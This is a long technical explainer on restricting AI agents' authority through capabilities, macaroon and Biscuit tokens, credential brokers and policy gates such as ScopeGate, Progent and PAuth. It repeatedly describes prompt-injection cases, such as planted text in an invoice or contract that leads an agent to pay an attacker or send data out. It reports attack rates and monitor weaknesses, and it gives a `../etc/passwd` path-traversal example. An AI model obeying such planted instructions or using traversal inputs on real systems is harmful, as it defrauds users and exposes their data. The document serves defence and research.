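In Semgrep's example, one report contains an instruction to delete all files. The agent tries to obey, but the server refuses because the agent has no capability for deleting. This protection works partly because the agent requested its access before reading the report. If it can request more access afterwards, the planted text can influence that request, and only the server's policy or a person can then stop it.

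The proposal has three migration phases. In the first, servers advertise capabilities, which clients may ignore if they declare that they do. In the second, servers accept capabilities, but a call without one still uses the agent's standing permissions. In the third, servers reject calls without a valid capability.

This gives developers time to adapt, but it offers little protection against prompt injection before the third phase. During the second phase, a misled agent could omit the capability and still do everything it could before, unless its host prevented this. Even in the third phase, Semgrep allows "legacy" grants for older services, and the example it gives permits every operation on every file.

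These capabilities also differ from object references. A call to read a report contains the ID of a capability for the whole folder and, in a separate field, the file's path. The file's name is again separate from the permission to read it, although the capability limits any damage to that folder.

### Turning a model's text back into references

A language model can't hold a reference because it only reads and writes text. The host has to give it a label for each reference and convert the label back when the model proposes a call.

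If the label is a long secret string that works as the capability itself, the model might copy it into an email, and anyone who read the email could use it. Miller and colleagues reject the common claim that capabilities inevitably spread out of control, but accept the argument behind it for systems that don't distinguish sending a capability from sending data. A safer label is a short name such as `payNorthgate`, which has meaning only in the table the host keeps for this agent. Unix file descriptors work the same way.

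Labels are harder to manage when one reference leads to many things. *String processing errors*, a discussion started by Karp (2026), considers a program with access to everything in a folder called `/data`. The program asks for `../etc/passwd`, in which `..` means "the folder above", and reaches a system file outside `/data`. Karp suggests that the folder's owner keep a table of permitted names, each with a reference to one file. The table would have an entry for `foo.txt` but not for `../etc/passwd`. Niyikiza, who works on permissions for agents' tools, describes this as selecting a resource from a set instead of constructing its name.

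Rice, another participant, objected that people would treat the table like an ordinary shared folder. They might share it with two colleagues, later add a file meant for only one of them, and forget that the other could read it too. Karp answered that they could make a separate table for each person, but this would work only if people knew they needed to. An agent with lasting access to an invoices folder raises the same problem, since it can read whatever anyone adds later.

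Niyikiza considers construction an open problem because the program may need something that does not exist yet and so cannot be referenced. In the invoice example, the user selects Northgate Paper from the saved payees but has to construct a payee for a new supplier.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) instead has the model write programs in Scala, which the agent submits through an MCP tool. The compiler checks which capabilities a program uses before the code runs. Programs can reach files, the network and other agents only through one library, and the system forbids language features, such as unsafe type conversions, that could hide a capability from the compiler. The approach depends on a checking feature of Scala that is still experimental. The compiler can establish that a program has access to a payment function, but not that the user wanted a particular payment.

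### Services that still use access lists

Banks, mail providers and file stores mostly identify an account and check what that account may do. A host can put wrappers in front of these services, but the wrappers help only if the agent has no other way in, such as a key stored where its commands can read it.

Code that the model writes can cause a similar problem. Miller uses the term "magic name" for a name that gives code access to something its creator didn't grant. For example, a host might run the model's code in an environment where a web request function is always available. Even if the host withheld every reference to mail and files, the code could still send the invoice's contents to an outside address.

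Wrappers also don't change what happens inside older software. Polaris could limit which files Excel received, but all of Excel's components and macros shared access to those files. Likewise, a bug in a mail server that logs in to a whole mailbox can expose all of it, even if each agent has a reference to only one message.

### The work of granting access

Operating systems could ask for confirmation whenever a program tries to do something sensitive, but Habitat Chronicles calls experience with this approach "pretty dismal", because people soon say yes without thinking. A powerbox avoids the extra question when the user has to pick a file anyway.

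That is often not true of an agent. Someone who asks an agent to pay an invoice may not want to look for the email. If the agent asks them to find it and choose the payee, it hasn't saved them much work.

Some tasks also need broad access, no matter how carefully people grant it. Miller calls email software the worst case among the programs ordinary users regularly run, because even the minimum authority it needs is a dangerous combination. An agent that answers a whole inbox has to read strangers' messages and send replies.

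For narrower tasks, the host could choose the references from the user's request. If the user asked it to "pay this month's invoice from the paper supplier," the host might give the agent one wrapper that reads recent messages from Northgate Paper's saved address and another that pays the supplier's saved account. The user wouldn't have to pick anything, and the agent couldn't access the contracts. But the host would have to work out what the task required from one English sentence, before the agent had read any of the supplier's email.

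## Tokens that can only be narrowed, and brokers that hold the credentials

The JavaScript runtime protects the limits in the `onePayment` wrapper only against programs it runs itself. If a sub-agent on another company's computer is to make the payment, the host can send it only a string of bytes, which the sub-agent can copy or edit. The payment server therefore needs a way to detect whether anyone has widened the permission.

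*Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) describes three ways to give someone limited access to a distant service. The host can relay every request itself, which adds delay and requires it to stay online. It can ask for a new, narrower credential each time, as in OAuth token exchange. Or it can use a macaroon, a token that its holder can narrow without contacting anyone.

### Three restrictions on one payment

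A macaroon contains an identifier, a list of restrictions called caveats, and a signature. The signature comes from HMAC, a function that turns a key and a message into a short code. Anyone with the key can recompute the code. Without the key, nobody can practically produce the right code for a different message, and the code doesn't reveal the key.

For the invoice, the signatures would be:

```
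s0 = HMAC(secret key, "token 7f3a")
s1 = HMAC(s0, "payee = Northgate Paper's saved account")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "amount <= 500 GBP")
s3 = HMAC(s2, "time < 18:00 today")
```

The payment server computes `s0` with a key that only it has, and gives the host the identifier and `s0`. At this point the token allows any payment the user could make. The host adds the three caveats, using each signature as the key for the next. It then sends the sub-agent the identifier, the caveats and `s3`, but keeps the earlier signatures.

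When the sub-agent asks to pay £480, it includes the macaroon in the request. The server uses the identifier to find its secret key, recomputes the chain from the listed caveats and compares the result with `s3`. If they match, it checks that the request satisfies every caveat. A sub-agent that tried to change the token would get these results:

| Attempt | Result |
| --- | --- |
| Add "amount <= 100 GBP" | Works: the sub-agent uses `s3` as the key and gets a valid, narrower token |
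| Delete the expiry | Fails: the signature would have to be `s2`, which the sub-agent doesn't have |
| Replace the payee | Fails: the sub-agent would need `s0` to rebuild the chain |
| Add "amount <= 5000 GBP" | Has no effect: the £500 limit still applies |

Macaroons are bearer tokens, so a thief could use this one, but only to pay Northgate Paper.

The caveats limit each request but not the total, so the sub-agent could pay Northgate Paper £500 repeatedly until 18:00. `onePayment` prevented this by recording that it had been used. Here, the payment server would have to keep that record. Birgisson and colleagues suggest that a service can store macaroon identifiers in a database and revoke a macaroon by deleting its row, so the payment server could delete the row after the first payment.

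A caveat can also require proof from a third party, such as approval from the user's phone. To add this caveat, the host would choose a new key and encrypt it twice, once for the phone and once for the payment server. After the user approves, the phone would use that key to sign a second macaroon, which the sub-agent would send along with the first. The payment server can check the approval without any prior relationship with the phone.

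### Biscuit and public keys

Only the service that issued a macaroon can check it, because checking requires the secret key, and anyone with that key could also remove the caveats. This is a drawback if, for example, the bank behind the payment server also wants to check the token.

Biscuit is a later format that uses public-key signatures. Its token is a series of signed blocks, and each signature covers the block's content and a public key for the next block. The holder has the matching private key and can use it to sign one more block of restrictions. *Crate biscuit_auth* on Docs.rs explains that anyone with the issuer's public key can verify the whole token, but that key doesn't let them create or alter one.

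The formats also differ in how they express restrictions. A macaroon's caveat can be any text, and each service has to decide what it means. Clever Cloud's *Biscuit, the foundation for your authorization systems* (2021) describes this as difficult for developers and gives it as the reason Biscuit has a logic language instead. The invoice restrictions could look like this:

```
check if payee("northgate-paper");
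check if amount($a), $a <= 500;
check if time($t), $t < 2026-12-05T18:00:00Z;
```

The payment server takes the payee and amount from the request and the time from its own clock, then runs the checks.

Adding a caveat to a macaroon is faster than token exchange, but the difference hardly matters for agents today. Veski, Guerraoui and Froelicher (2026), in *CAPMAS*, measured about 0.01 milliseconds to add a caveat and 0.3 milliseconds to get a narrower token by exchange. A complete request in their test system took 10.8 seconds on average, including about 10 seconds for the language models.

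### Passing work to a sub-agent

Agents often divide a job among other agents. *AIP* (2026) points out that the holder of an OAuth token can't narrow it before passing it on, because only the authorization server can do that, so it's easy to just pass on the whole token. *Delegation Without Trust* found that three popular agent frameworks (LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen) don't limit what a sub-agent can do by default.

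Veski and colleagues use macaroons to narrow access at each step. In their example, a user asks for the salary of a project's leader. The coordinating agent has a token for both project and personnel records. It restricts a copy of the token to project records and sends it to a projects agent, which reports that Sara leads the project. The coordinator then restricts a second copy of the original token to personnel records and sends it to a personnel agent, which looks up Sara's salary.

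Every agent must add a caveat listing what the next agent may do, and the system rejects any request that lacks one. Veski and colleagues considered having agents list what the next one may *not* do, but an agent that forgot to do so would pass on all its permissions.

Macaroons don't ensure that a coordinator delegates sensibly. A coordinator under an attacker's influence could still give a sub-agent its entire token, but no more authority than that token grants.

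Some systems forbid agents to delegate. *Delegated Authority Problem Space Report*, a Decentralized Identity Foundation draft by Bucci, Caballero and colleagues, argues that this makes things worse. An agent can get around the ban by sharing its secret with another agent, which may unlock much more than the task needs, or by making requests on that agent's behalf. Either way, the logs no longer show who did what.

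### Union and intersection

A sub-agent may also have permissions of its own. Suppose the main agent passes the invoice to a company's finance agent, and their permissions are:

- Main agent, for this task: A = {read invoice, pay supplier}
- Finance agent: B = {pay supplier, pay staff, read past payments}

If each agent uses its own permissions for whatever the other requests, together they can do anything in the union, A ∪ B = {read invoice, pay supplier, pay staff, read past payments}. Planted text in the invoice could then lead the main agent to request a salary payment, and the finance agent would make it even though it was never part of the user's task.

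If the finance agent may do only what both sets allow, its permissions are A ∩ B = {pay supplier}, and it refuses the salary payment. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (Tallam, 2026) extends this rule to chains of any length. If K₀ is the user's set of permissions and K₁ to Kₙ are those of the agents along the chain, the last agent may use only the unexpired permissions in K₀ ∩ K₁ ∩ … ∩ Kₙ, so adding an agent can remove permissions but never add them.

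Tallam argues that the rule prevents confused deputies because a deputy can never do more than its caller. The rule does stop an employee from using an agent to get everyone's salaries. But if the sets contain permissions as broad as "create payments", their intersection still allows a payment to the attacker's account.

The intersection can also exclude permissions the task needs. The finance agent should compare the account number on the invoice with past payments, but A doesn't include permission to read them. Hardy's compiler would have had the same problem with its statistics file, which customers had no permission to write. The user could add the missing permission to the task. Or the finance agent could do the comparison under its own authority and return only whether the numbers match, provided the caller can't use that check to extract other information.

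*Delegation Without Trust* simulated 2,000 random cases in which an attacker controlled a sub-agent in a system with 8,100 possible actions. With an ordinary shared token, the attacker could perform all 8,100. With tokens narrowed at each step, the attacker could perform only 1.5 on average, which was the average size of the tasks the simulation assigned. This shows how much narrowing can achieve, but real systems also have to work out which actions a task requires.

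### DelegateGuard and cancelled tasks

Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues (2026), in *DelegateGuard*, built a monitor that checks every action by which an agent moves data. The monitor keeps a table of grants, each of which specifies:

- the agent that holds it and the purpose it is for;
- the kinds of data, operations and destinations it covers;
- how many more times agents may delegate it;
- whether someone has revoked it.

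An agent can create a grant for a sub-agent only if the new grant stays within its own on every point.

In the main example, a user asks for a summary of a confidential contract, and the main agent gives the formatting to a worker. The worker may transform the text and send it only to the user. The contract contains a planted instruction to send its terms to an outside web address. The monitor blocks this because that address isn't in the worker's grant. It would also stop the main agent from creating a worker that could send data there.

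The monitor also handles work still queued when the user cancels a task. A worker may start that work minutes later with a token that still looks valid. A macaroon or Biscuit works until it expires unless the service checks an outside record, and *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025) describes offline revocation of such tokens as still being explored. In DelegateGuard, revoking a grant also revokes every grant derived from it, much as switching off a revocable forwarder cuts off everyone who shares it. The monitor rechecks the whole chain of grants when the worker tries to act. This works only if all the agents' actions go through the monitor.

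Tran-Truong and colleagues ran several tests:

| Test | Comparison | DelegateGuard |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Agents working over several turns, with planted text | No monitor: 38 of 45 runs leaked data | 9 of 45 leaked |
| Worker acts after the user cancels | List of allowed destinations: 5 of 5 actions went ahead | 0 of 5 |
| Worker sends the wrong kind of data to an allowed destination | List of allowed destinations: 5 of 5 went ahead | 0 of 5 |
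| 26 attacks, most designed to stay within the agent's permissions | No monitor: 18 leaked data | 3 leaked |

In the multi-turn test, DelegateGuard also let all 45 harmless tasks finish. The comparison without a monitor is weak evidence about leading models in late 2026, because the agents ran on Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model. In a separate test, that model attempted what the attacker wanted in 42 of 45 cases. The monitor applies the same rules whichever model is running.

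All nine leaks in the multi-turn test came from code review, where the agent's job was to post comments that outsiders could read. The monitor checks the kind of data and its destination but not the text, so if it allows an ordinary review comment, it also allows one containing a secret. Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that any monitor that ignores content has this weakness wherever an allowed destination is visible to the attacker. A filter that searched outgoing text for the secret stopped these leaks but also blocked four of five legitimate tasks.

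The "purpose" in a grant is a label such as `contract.summarize/format`, and the monitor checks only that the action's label falls under the one in the grant. Attackers who chose misleading labels gained nothing in the tests, because the limits on data and destinations still applied. Those limits therefore seem to provide most of the protection, and they have to be right from the start. When the initial grant was tested with one convenient outside address added, 30 of 45 attacks succeeded.

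### Keeping the real credential in a broker

Some services accept only an ordinary API key or password, so an agent can't use a narrowed token with them directly. A credential broker, like the vault and proxy in Anthropic's hosted agents, keeps the real credential and adds it to each request. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a broker that runs beside each agent in a healthcare company's system and also limits how often the agent can make requests, how much it can send and which services it can reach.

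Brokers may be necessary even for narrow tokens. Macaroons and Biscuits depend on secrets, and Bucci and colleagues doubt that a language model can keep a secret if someone asks for it cleverly enough. Karp, who edited their report, proposes keeping the secrets from the agent and having a conventional program use them at the agent's request.

In *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026) tested a broker sold by their employer, Corvic AI. Code in the agent's environment successfully called GitHub through the broker. They then looked for the credential in the environment's settings, in common file locations and in the request before it left. They also called three websites that send back whatever they receive, to see whether the broker would attach the credential to requests for the wrong site. All 16 checks gave the secure result.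 The test was small and run by the product's own makers, and it didn't cover redirects, which might carry a credential to another site.

Like Anthropic's proxy, such a broker prevents theft of the credential but not its misuse, so the wrong payment would still go through. Kenney and colleagues acknowledge this limit. On their own 25-point scale, which reflects their judgement rather than measurements, the broker reduced the risk of stolen credentials in the agent's environment from 20 to 4, but the risk from excessive permissions only from 20 to 15.

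A broker can also issue a separate short-lived credential for each operation. Hartman's *Your AI Agent Is an Easily Confused Deputy* proposes a design in which one component approves requests and another holds the credentials, so that an attacker has to break into both. His example is an agent that reads server statistics, queries a database, opens a support ticket and posts to Slack. The broker gives it a 60-second token to read the statistics. Hartman argues that an attacker who takes over the agent at that moment can't reach the other three services, because their tokens don't exist yet.

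That is true of someone who steals the token, but an attacker who controls the agent can make it request another. The agent writes its own description of what it needs, and the broker normally approves such requests because they are part of the agent's job. Hartman's design requires a person to approve riskier operations, which would protect the payment if that person noticed the wrong account number.

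### When the broker is the confused deputy

A broker that serves many users has more authority than any one of them. Suppose two companies share a broker, and an agent working for the first asks to use "the payments connection for company 2". If the broker checks only that the request comes from a registered agent, it will add company 2's credential to the request. As at Tymshare, the agent only has to name the connection, because the broker supplies the permission to use it.

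Hartman describes a similar flaw in Microsoft Defender for Cloud, a security service with access to many customers' cloud accounts. In February 2024, two instructors at the SANS Institute, a security training organization, reported that under certain conditions the service could disclose one customer's security findings to outsiders. Microsoft rated the flaw critical.

The remedy, as proposed for Meta's assistant, is for the broker to take the company's identity from the authenticated session and ignore any company named in the request. The broker could also give each agent references only to that agent's own connections. An agent working for one user would still need narrower limits for each task.

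Brokers are also targets for theft because they hold many credentials in one place. In March 2026, attackers compromised LiteLLM, a gateway that many companies use to store their keys for AI services. Hartman reports an estimate of 500,000 affected corporate identities. This was not a confused-deputy attack, because the attackers stole the credentials outright.

### A valid token in the wrong task

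Suppose the host gives the agent the macaroon for Northgate Paper but the agent hasn't used it yet. That afternoon, the user asks the agent to summarize some new messages. One claims to be from Northgate Paper and demands £400 for an extra delivery, and the agent pays. The payment meets the macaroon's caveats on payee, amount and expiry, but the user had authorized a payment for a different job.

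Gallo argues that this is a general weakness of systems that rely on possession of a token. A system that checks only the operation and the resource must give the same answer to two requests that differ only in the chain of steps that led to them, even if the user asked for one and a stranger prompted the other. Tying a token to a particular agent doesn't help, because that agent makes both requests.

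Gallo's alternative, Proof-of-Continuity, requires each step to prove that it follows from the previous step and to use no more authority than the previous step had. The afternoon's task would start with permission only to read messages, so no later step in it could make a payment, even though the agent has a payment token from another task.

Binding a token to its task achieves much of this. The host could add a fourth caveat, "task = 4127", and the payment server would reject the token in a request from any other task. The host has to attach the task number itself, since a misled model could write 4127. Existing systems use similar bindings. Veski and colleagues put a request number in every macaroon, and *CapSeal* (2026) ties an agent's capabilities to one session. Gallo accepts that such tokens can overcome the objection, as long as the service checks the context when it decides. He leaves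 open how to build the proofs his own model needs.

People sometimes want an agent to combine permissions from different sources, and strict separation between tasks can prevent this. Bucci and colleagues therefore treat continuity as an optional restriction, useful where an accidental combination could do serious harm. They also warn that agents can bypass it in the same ways they can bypass a ban on delegation.

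The binding makes no difference within a single task. The wrong payment in the invoice example would have the right task number, so only the payee caveat would stop it.

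## Deciding how much authority a task needs

A payee caveat stops the wrong payment only if whoever adds it knows the right payee. Wrappers, grants and scopes also depend on someone choosing the right limit. The limit could come from the operator (the company or developer that deploys the agent), the user, or a language model that works out the necessary permissions from the user's request.

### A policy written in advance

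An attacker has the least influence over an operator's fixed policy, because the operator writes it before the agent reads anything. But one policy has to serve many tasks. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) describes a coding assistant that connects to GitHub with a broad access token. The assistant can use about 40 tools, 16 of which can write, in every repository its user can access. It needs only two read-only tools to summarize the open issues in one repository. A token limited to reading that repository would have prevented the GitHub attack that Invariant Labs demonstrated, but the assistant couldn't use it to fix a failing build, which the user might ask for next.

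Many agents have no policy for the values in a tool call. In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) audited the public code of three software kits for building agents: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to Stripe's payment services. The paper distinguishes between exposing a tool, which makes it available to the model, and authorizing a call, which means deciding whether a specific payment may go ahead, given its amount and the receiving account.

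All three kits let developers choose which tools to expose, but none authorizes individual calls by default. LangGraph, for example, finds the tool by name, usually checks that the arguments have the right form, and runs it, so an attacker's account number would pass the check. The Stripe kit also has a list of permitted actions and can use a restricted key, but within those limits it passes on whatever amount and customer the model supplies.

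A developer who connects a payment tool and relies on the defaults has built a confused deputy, though Mellafe Zuvic does not call the defaults software flaws. Developers can add their own checks or ask a person to approve calls. The audit did not cover Stripe's remote MCP server, which may have further checks.

### How often models attempt such calls

Mellafe Zuvic also reports how often 27 models attempted an unauthorized call after reading planted text that presented the call as part of the user's task. The mean rate was 0.603 for 12 cheaper models and 0.189 for 15 flagship models. Rates varied widely within each group, and across all the models they ranged from 0 for a preview of Gemini 3.1 Pro to 1 for GPT-4o mini.

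In separate tests, Mistral Large attempted the call in 2.7% of trials when the planted text was crude and in 45.9% when the text fitted the task.

These are attempts in a sandbox, not successful thefts. The wording tests used one author's single-turn scenarios. Mellafe Zuvic infers from price that companies use the cheaper models for high-volume work, but has no data on which models they run. The inference is plausible, and if it is right, results for the best models may understate the risk in ordinary products.

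### ScopeGate's five checks

Mellafe Zuvic's remedy is ScopeGate, a conventional program that sits between the model and the tools. It compares each proposed call with the operator's policy in five steps:

1. Scope: the policy must list the tool.
2. Authorization: any restricted argument, such as the account to pay, must have an approved value.
3. Money: the amount must be a real number between zero and a ceiling.
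4. Idempotency: a call that changes something may need a key, supplied from outside the model, that helps the service recognize a repeated request.
5. Default deny: ScopeGate refuses any call that hasn't passed every check, including one that causes an error in ScopeGate itself.

In the main demonstration, a model's output proposed changing a merchant's payout account to the attacker's. LangChain's default code made the change, but ScopeGate refused the same call. ScopeGate also refused all 48 calls in a prepared set of evasions, including lookalike characters, altered tool names and strange amounts. That set had exposed a bug in an earlier version, which accepted NaN ("not a number") as an amount because NaN is never greater than the ceiling. In another test, a model acting as the attacker learned why each call had failed and tried again. It made 29 unauthorized attempts in 40 rounds, and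 none succeeded.

The tests give much less evidence about how often ScopeGate would refuse legitimate calls. It allowed all ten in the main control test, but a gate that refused a quarter of legitimate calls would still allow all ten about 6% of the time (0.75^10 ≈ 0.06).

The security results also follow almost directly from the design, because a program checked the attacker's account against the approved list and the account was not on it. Keeping the list correct is harder, so Mellafe Zuvic requires that no part of the policy come from a model's output, even indirectly. If an email persuaded a bookkeeping agent to replace a supplier's bank details with the attacker's, and ScopeGate took its approved accounts from those records, the attacker's account would pass every check.

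For the invoice, a ScopeGate policy could allow payments only to saved payees and only up to £500. This would stop the payment to the attacker's account, but it would also block payments to new suppliers. A misleading email could still cause a £500 payment to the wrong saved payee.

### Asking the user

The user knows more about the task than the operator does, so many products ask the user for approval. *MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) reports four arrangements. Claude asked before every call to a server that the user had added. Codex asked only before riskier operations, such as network access. ChatGPT's and Claude's built-in connectors asked once, when the user connected the service. Many custom agents never asked, and their developers often gave them too much access because it was convenient.

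An attacker can't click "approve", but can influence what the agent requests and how it explains the request. The attacker also benefits from approval fatigue, the habit of approving requests without reading them. Parkinson and colleagues cite a company's report that users of its coding agent approved 93% of permission prompts. That rate doesn't prove carelessness, since most of the requests may have been fine, but users who rightly approve almost every request can easily approve a harmful one too.

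MiniScope reduces the number of prompts by asking about groups of operations. It uses the OAuth scopes that services already publish, and works as follows:

1. The agent submits a plan that lists the calls it expects to make.
2. MiniScope finds the cheapest set of scopes that covers the plan, where a scope's cost is the number of methods (individual operations) it permits.
3. If the user hasn't already granted those scopes, MiniScope asks. The user can allow them once, for this session or always, or refuse.
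4. MiniScope checks each call against the granted scopes and attaches the real credential only if the call is covered.

Step 2 is an optimization problem. Let x_v be 1 if MiniScope selects scope v and 0 if it doesn't. MiniScope minimizes the sum of cost(v) · x_v over all scopes, while ensuring that at least one selected scope permits each planned call. It can't just take the narrowest scope for each call, because several scopes may permit the same call and one of them may cover several calls. In Google Calendar, 24 of 37 methods have more than one route through the hierarchy of scopes.

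Zhu and colleagues illustrate the protection with a user who asks the agent to reply to an email about an event. The email contains a planted instruction to delete it afterwards. After reading it, the agent makes a new plan that requires full access to Gmail, which an attentive user can refuse. However, the agent needed further permission anyway to send the reply, so the user was expecting a request and would have to notice that this one was too broad.

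In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, MiniScope asked for confirmation on 18% to 60% of requests, depending on the simulated user's habits. One simulated user, played by a language model, confirmed requests a quarter as often as it did under a system that asked about each method separately. No real people took part, so the simulation estimates how many prompts users would see but not how carefully they would read them. A simulated user who always chose "always allow" soon stopped seeing prompts and lost the protection they provided.

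The calculation in step 2 is useful even without prompts. Zhu and colleagues used it to check connectors in ChatGPT and Claude in late 2025 and found six that requested more access than their tools needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector requested permission for 50 methods when it needed only 32. The extra access let it change and delete emails, although it was described in the product as read-only.

MiniScope doesn't protect against attacks that stay within a granted scope, so it would not stop the wrong payment. Zhu and colleagues could have made it prompt users about individual recipients, but decided against this to avoid approval fatigue.

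### Letting a model write the policy

A model can write a narrow policy for each task without asking anyone. If the model sees only the user's request, a stranger's email can't influence the policy. But the request often leaves out a detail the policy needs, such as a supplier's account number, and that detail may be in the email.

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, let the policy change as the agent learns more, with restrictions on how it can change. A Progent policy is a list of rules about tools and their arguments. For the invoice, it might amount to this:

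```
allow search_mail     when sender = the paper supplier
allow create_payment  when payee is in saved payees and amount <= 500
```

A conventional program checks every call against the rules and refuses calls that no rule allows. After a call, a model decides whether the result might require a policy change. It decides without seeing the result, which may contain planted text. If the answer is yes, the model reads the result and proposes a new policy.

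Next, a solver (software that settles logical questions) compares the two policies. The new policy takes effect automatically only if it allows no calls that the old one didn't. Any other change is an expansion and needs approval.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026), a review that covers Progent, warned that planted text could cause an update to relax the restrictions. The solver addresses this by flagging a broader policy as an expansion, though planted text may still lead the model to propose one.

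A change that only narrows the policy can still help an attacker. Suppose the first policy allows a payment to any account, because the user's request didn't give one. The model then reads the planted email and proposes a policy that allows payment only to the attacker's account. The new policy is narrower, so it takes effect without approval. Limiting the first policy to saved payees would prevent this, because paying the attacker would then require expanding the policy.

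Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a public benchmark where agents do banking, travel, Slack and office tasks and encounter planted instructions as they work. Attacks succeeded in 39.9% of cases without a defence and in 1.0% with Progent, and agents using Progent completed about as many tasks as without it. On a second benchmark, ASB, the attack success rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%.

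In these tests, the system approved every expansion automatically to simulate a careless user. The 1.0% therefore reflects how well a model wrote policies, not how much the solver's guarantee adds. The first policy alone, with no updates, reduced successful attacks on AgentDojo to 2.5%. No attacks succeeded under the assumption that a careful person reviewed the first policy and every expansion and would notice a malicious address. Only 6% of proposed updates were expansions, so a person would have had few to review.

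The agents mostly ran on GPT-4o, an old model by late 2026. Claude Sonnet 4 was more resistant. Attacks on it succeeded in 6.8% of cases without Progent and 0.5% with it. Shi and colleagues also excluded two attacks that persuaded an agent to choose a different but legitimate hotel, because a policy that allows hotel bookings would also allow booking that hotel.

Models don't always choose the smallest permission, even when nobody is attacking them. Zhu and colleagues gave models a plan and a list of scopes and asked for the minimum scopes the plan needed. Proprietary models such as GPT-5 matched MiniScope's answer in 70% to 83% of cases, and open models in 20% to 34%. The models tested are about a year old or more, but the comparison shows why one might leave this choice to a conventional solver.

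### Treating the request as the authorization

Sharma, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond OAuth*, have each server work out which calls the user's request implies. Their system, PAuth, treats the request itself as permission for exactly those calls. In their main example, the user asks an agent to pay a quarter of a Citi credit card balance from a Chase bank account, but only if the balance is over $1,000. The steps are:

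1. The user signs the text of the request, so the agent can't change it, and each bank receives a copy.
2. At each bank, a language model translates the request into a short program. It sees the request and the descriptions of the tools, but no outside text.
3. Conventional software extracts the part of the program that determines the bank's own call, which Sharma and colleagues call a slice. Chase's slice says that the payee is Citi and the amount is the Citi balance divided by four, provided the balance is over $1,000.
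4. The agent asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns $1,200 in a signed "envelope" that also records which call produced the number.
5. The agent asks Chase to pay $300 and includes the envelope. Chase checks Citi's signature, repeats the calculation and makes the payment.

If planted text leads the agent to request $301 or another payee, the call doesn't match the slice, so Chase asks the user. Even an attacker with complete control of the agent can't forge Citi's signature. The user can also give permission before the payment amount is known, which RFC 9396 wouldn't allow.

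The test used 100 tasks, mostly adapted from AgentDojo, and 634 calls that departed from those tasks, for example by changing a recipient or skipping a condition. PAuth blocked all 634 calls, meaning that it asked the user. With the original wording, it let 71 of the 100 tasks through without a question. After Sharma and colleagues rewrote the unclear tasks to include every necessary detail, it let all 100 through.

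"Pay this month's invoice from the paper supplier" requires someone to read an email and find the amount. PAuth represents anything a model has to extract from text as an unknown that matches no value, so the payment server would ask the user. The agent could avoid the question by rewriting the request as something more specific, such as "Pay £480 to this account", and proposing that for the user to sign. If the account number came from planted text, the user would again be the only check. PAuth assumes that users carefully review every task before they submit it.

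PAuth also requires more from the servers. Each one has to run a language model that translates requests correctly, which cost $0.002 to $0.038 per task in the tests. Every server involved sees the full request, so a payment company might learn about other errands in the same message. Services could adopt PAuth one at a time, but those that hadn't would do no checking.

### When two permissions are both the smallest

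MiniScope looks for the least permission that covers a task, but there may be more than one. Suppose a task needs operation a, and one permission allows {a, b} while another allows {a, c, d}. If the service offers nothing narrower, both are minimal because neither set contains the other. Counting operations favours the first, but b might be "delete everything" while c and d only read public data.

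Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, looked for such cases in the permission tables that Microsoft and Google publish. One involves Microsoft Graph, the interface through which programs reach Microsoft 365 and related services. The task is to list and create OAuth permission grants, the records of what applications may do. Two permissions cover it:

| Permission | Endpoints it reaches | Microsoft's privilege level |
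| --- | --- | --- |
| `Directory.ReadWrite.All` | 355 | 4 |
| `DelegatedPermissionGrant.ReadWrite.All` | 11 | 4 |

An endpoint is a single operation that a program can request. Each permission reaches at least one endpoint that the other doesn't, so neither grants strictly less authority. Most administrators would presumably choose the one that reaches 11 endpoints, but Microsoft's four-point scale doesn't help them choose because it puts both at the highest level.

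The option that reaches the fewest endpoints may still let an agent change more. To manage application registrations, for example, an agent can use either one permission that reaches 243 endpoints, 153 of which change something, or two permissions that together reach 297 endpoints, only 20 of which change something. The better choice depends on whether the administrator is more worried about what the agent could read or alter. A cost function based on the number of methods, like MiniScope's, would favour the single permission and give the agent more than seven times as many ways to change things.

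Xu found no unique minimum for 29.8% to 33.3% of the Microsoft Graph tasks, depending on the type of access, and for 3.2% of the Google tasks. In the two main types of Graph access, Microsoft's scale gave both permissions the same level in 67.4% and 74.4% of the competing pairs. It also did so in about 61% of pairs where one permission contained the other, so the scale is coarse in general. Xu generated the tasks from the structure of the tables, so the rates describe the available permissions, not how often working agents face this choice.

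Xu also asked six leading models to choose from lists of sufficient permissions. They picked a minimal one in 99.0% of 1,708 decisions. But in 22.1% of decisions, another option was at least as good on all four measures of risk (operations, changes, services reached and administrative access) and better on at least one. A benchmark that checks only whether the agent chose a minimal permission would miss nearly all of these poor choices. Xu recommends showing the alternatives to whoever approves the access. That would, however, give people more to read in each prompt.

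### Forbidding dangerous combinations

An agent can end up with a dangerous combination of permissions even if each one was chosen carefully. Surapani and colleagues identify limiting combined authority as one of the main unsolved problems in authorizing agents. A simple way to limit it is to forbid certain combinations.

Willison warns against giving an agent the "lethal trifecta" of private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out. Removing any one of the three stops an attacker from stealing the data.

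Meta's "Rule of Two" allows an agent at most two of three properties similar to Willison's in one session. Parkinson and colleagues describe them as untrusted input, sensitive data, and the ability to communicate externally or change something. The third is broader than Willison's version because it includes making a payment or deleting a file.

The invoice agent has all three properties, and its mail server alone supplies them. Disconnecting the other servers would therefore protect the contracts and the bank account but not the rest of the mail. The user would have to remove particular operations:

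| What the user removes | Theft of the contracts | Wrong payment | Work the agent can no longer do |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Untrusted text: the user types the amount and picks a saved payee | Prevented | Prevented | Find and read the invoice |
| Private data: the agent sees only the invoice email | Prevented | Still possible | Search the mailbox or compare past payments |
| Sending and changing: the agent only prepares a payment for the user to make | Prevented | Prevented only if the user notices the wrong account | Make the payment or reply to the supplier |

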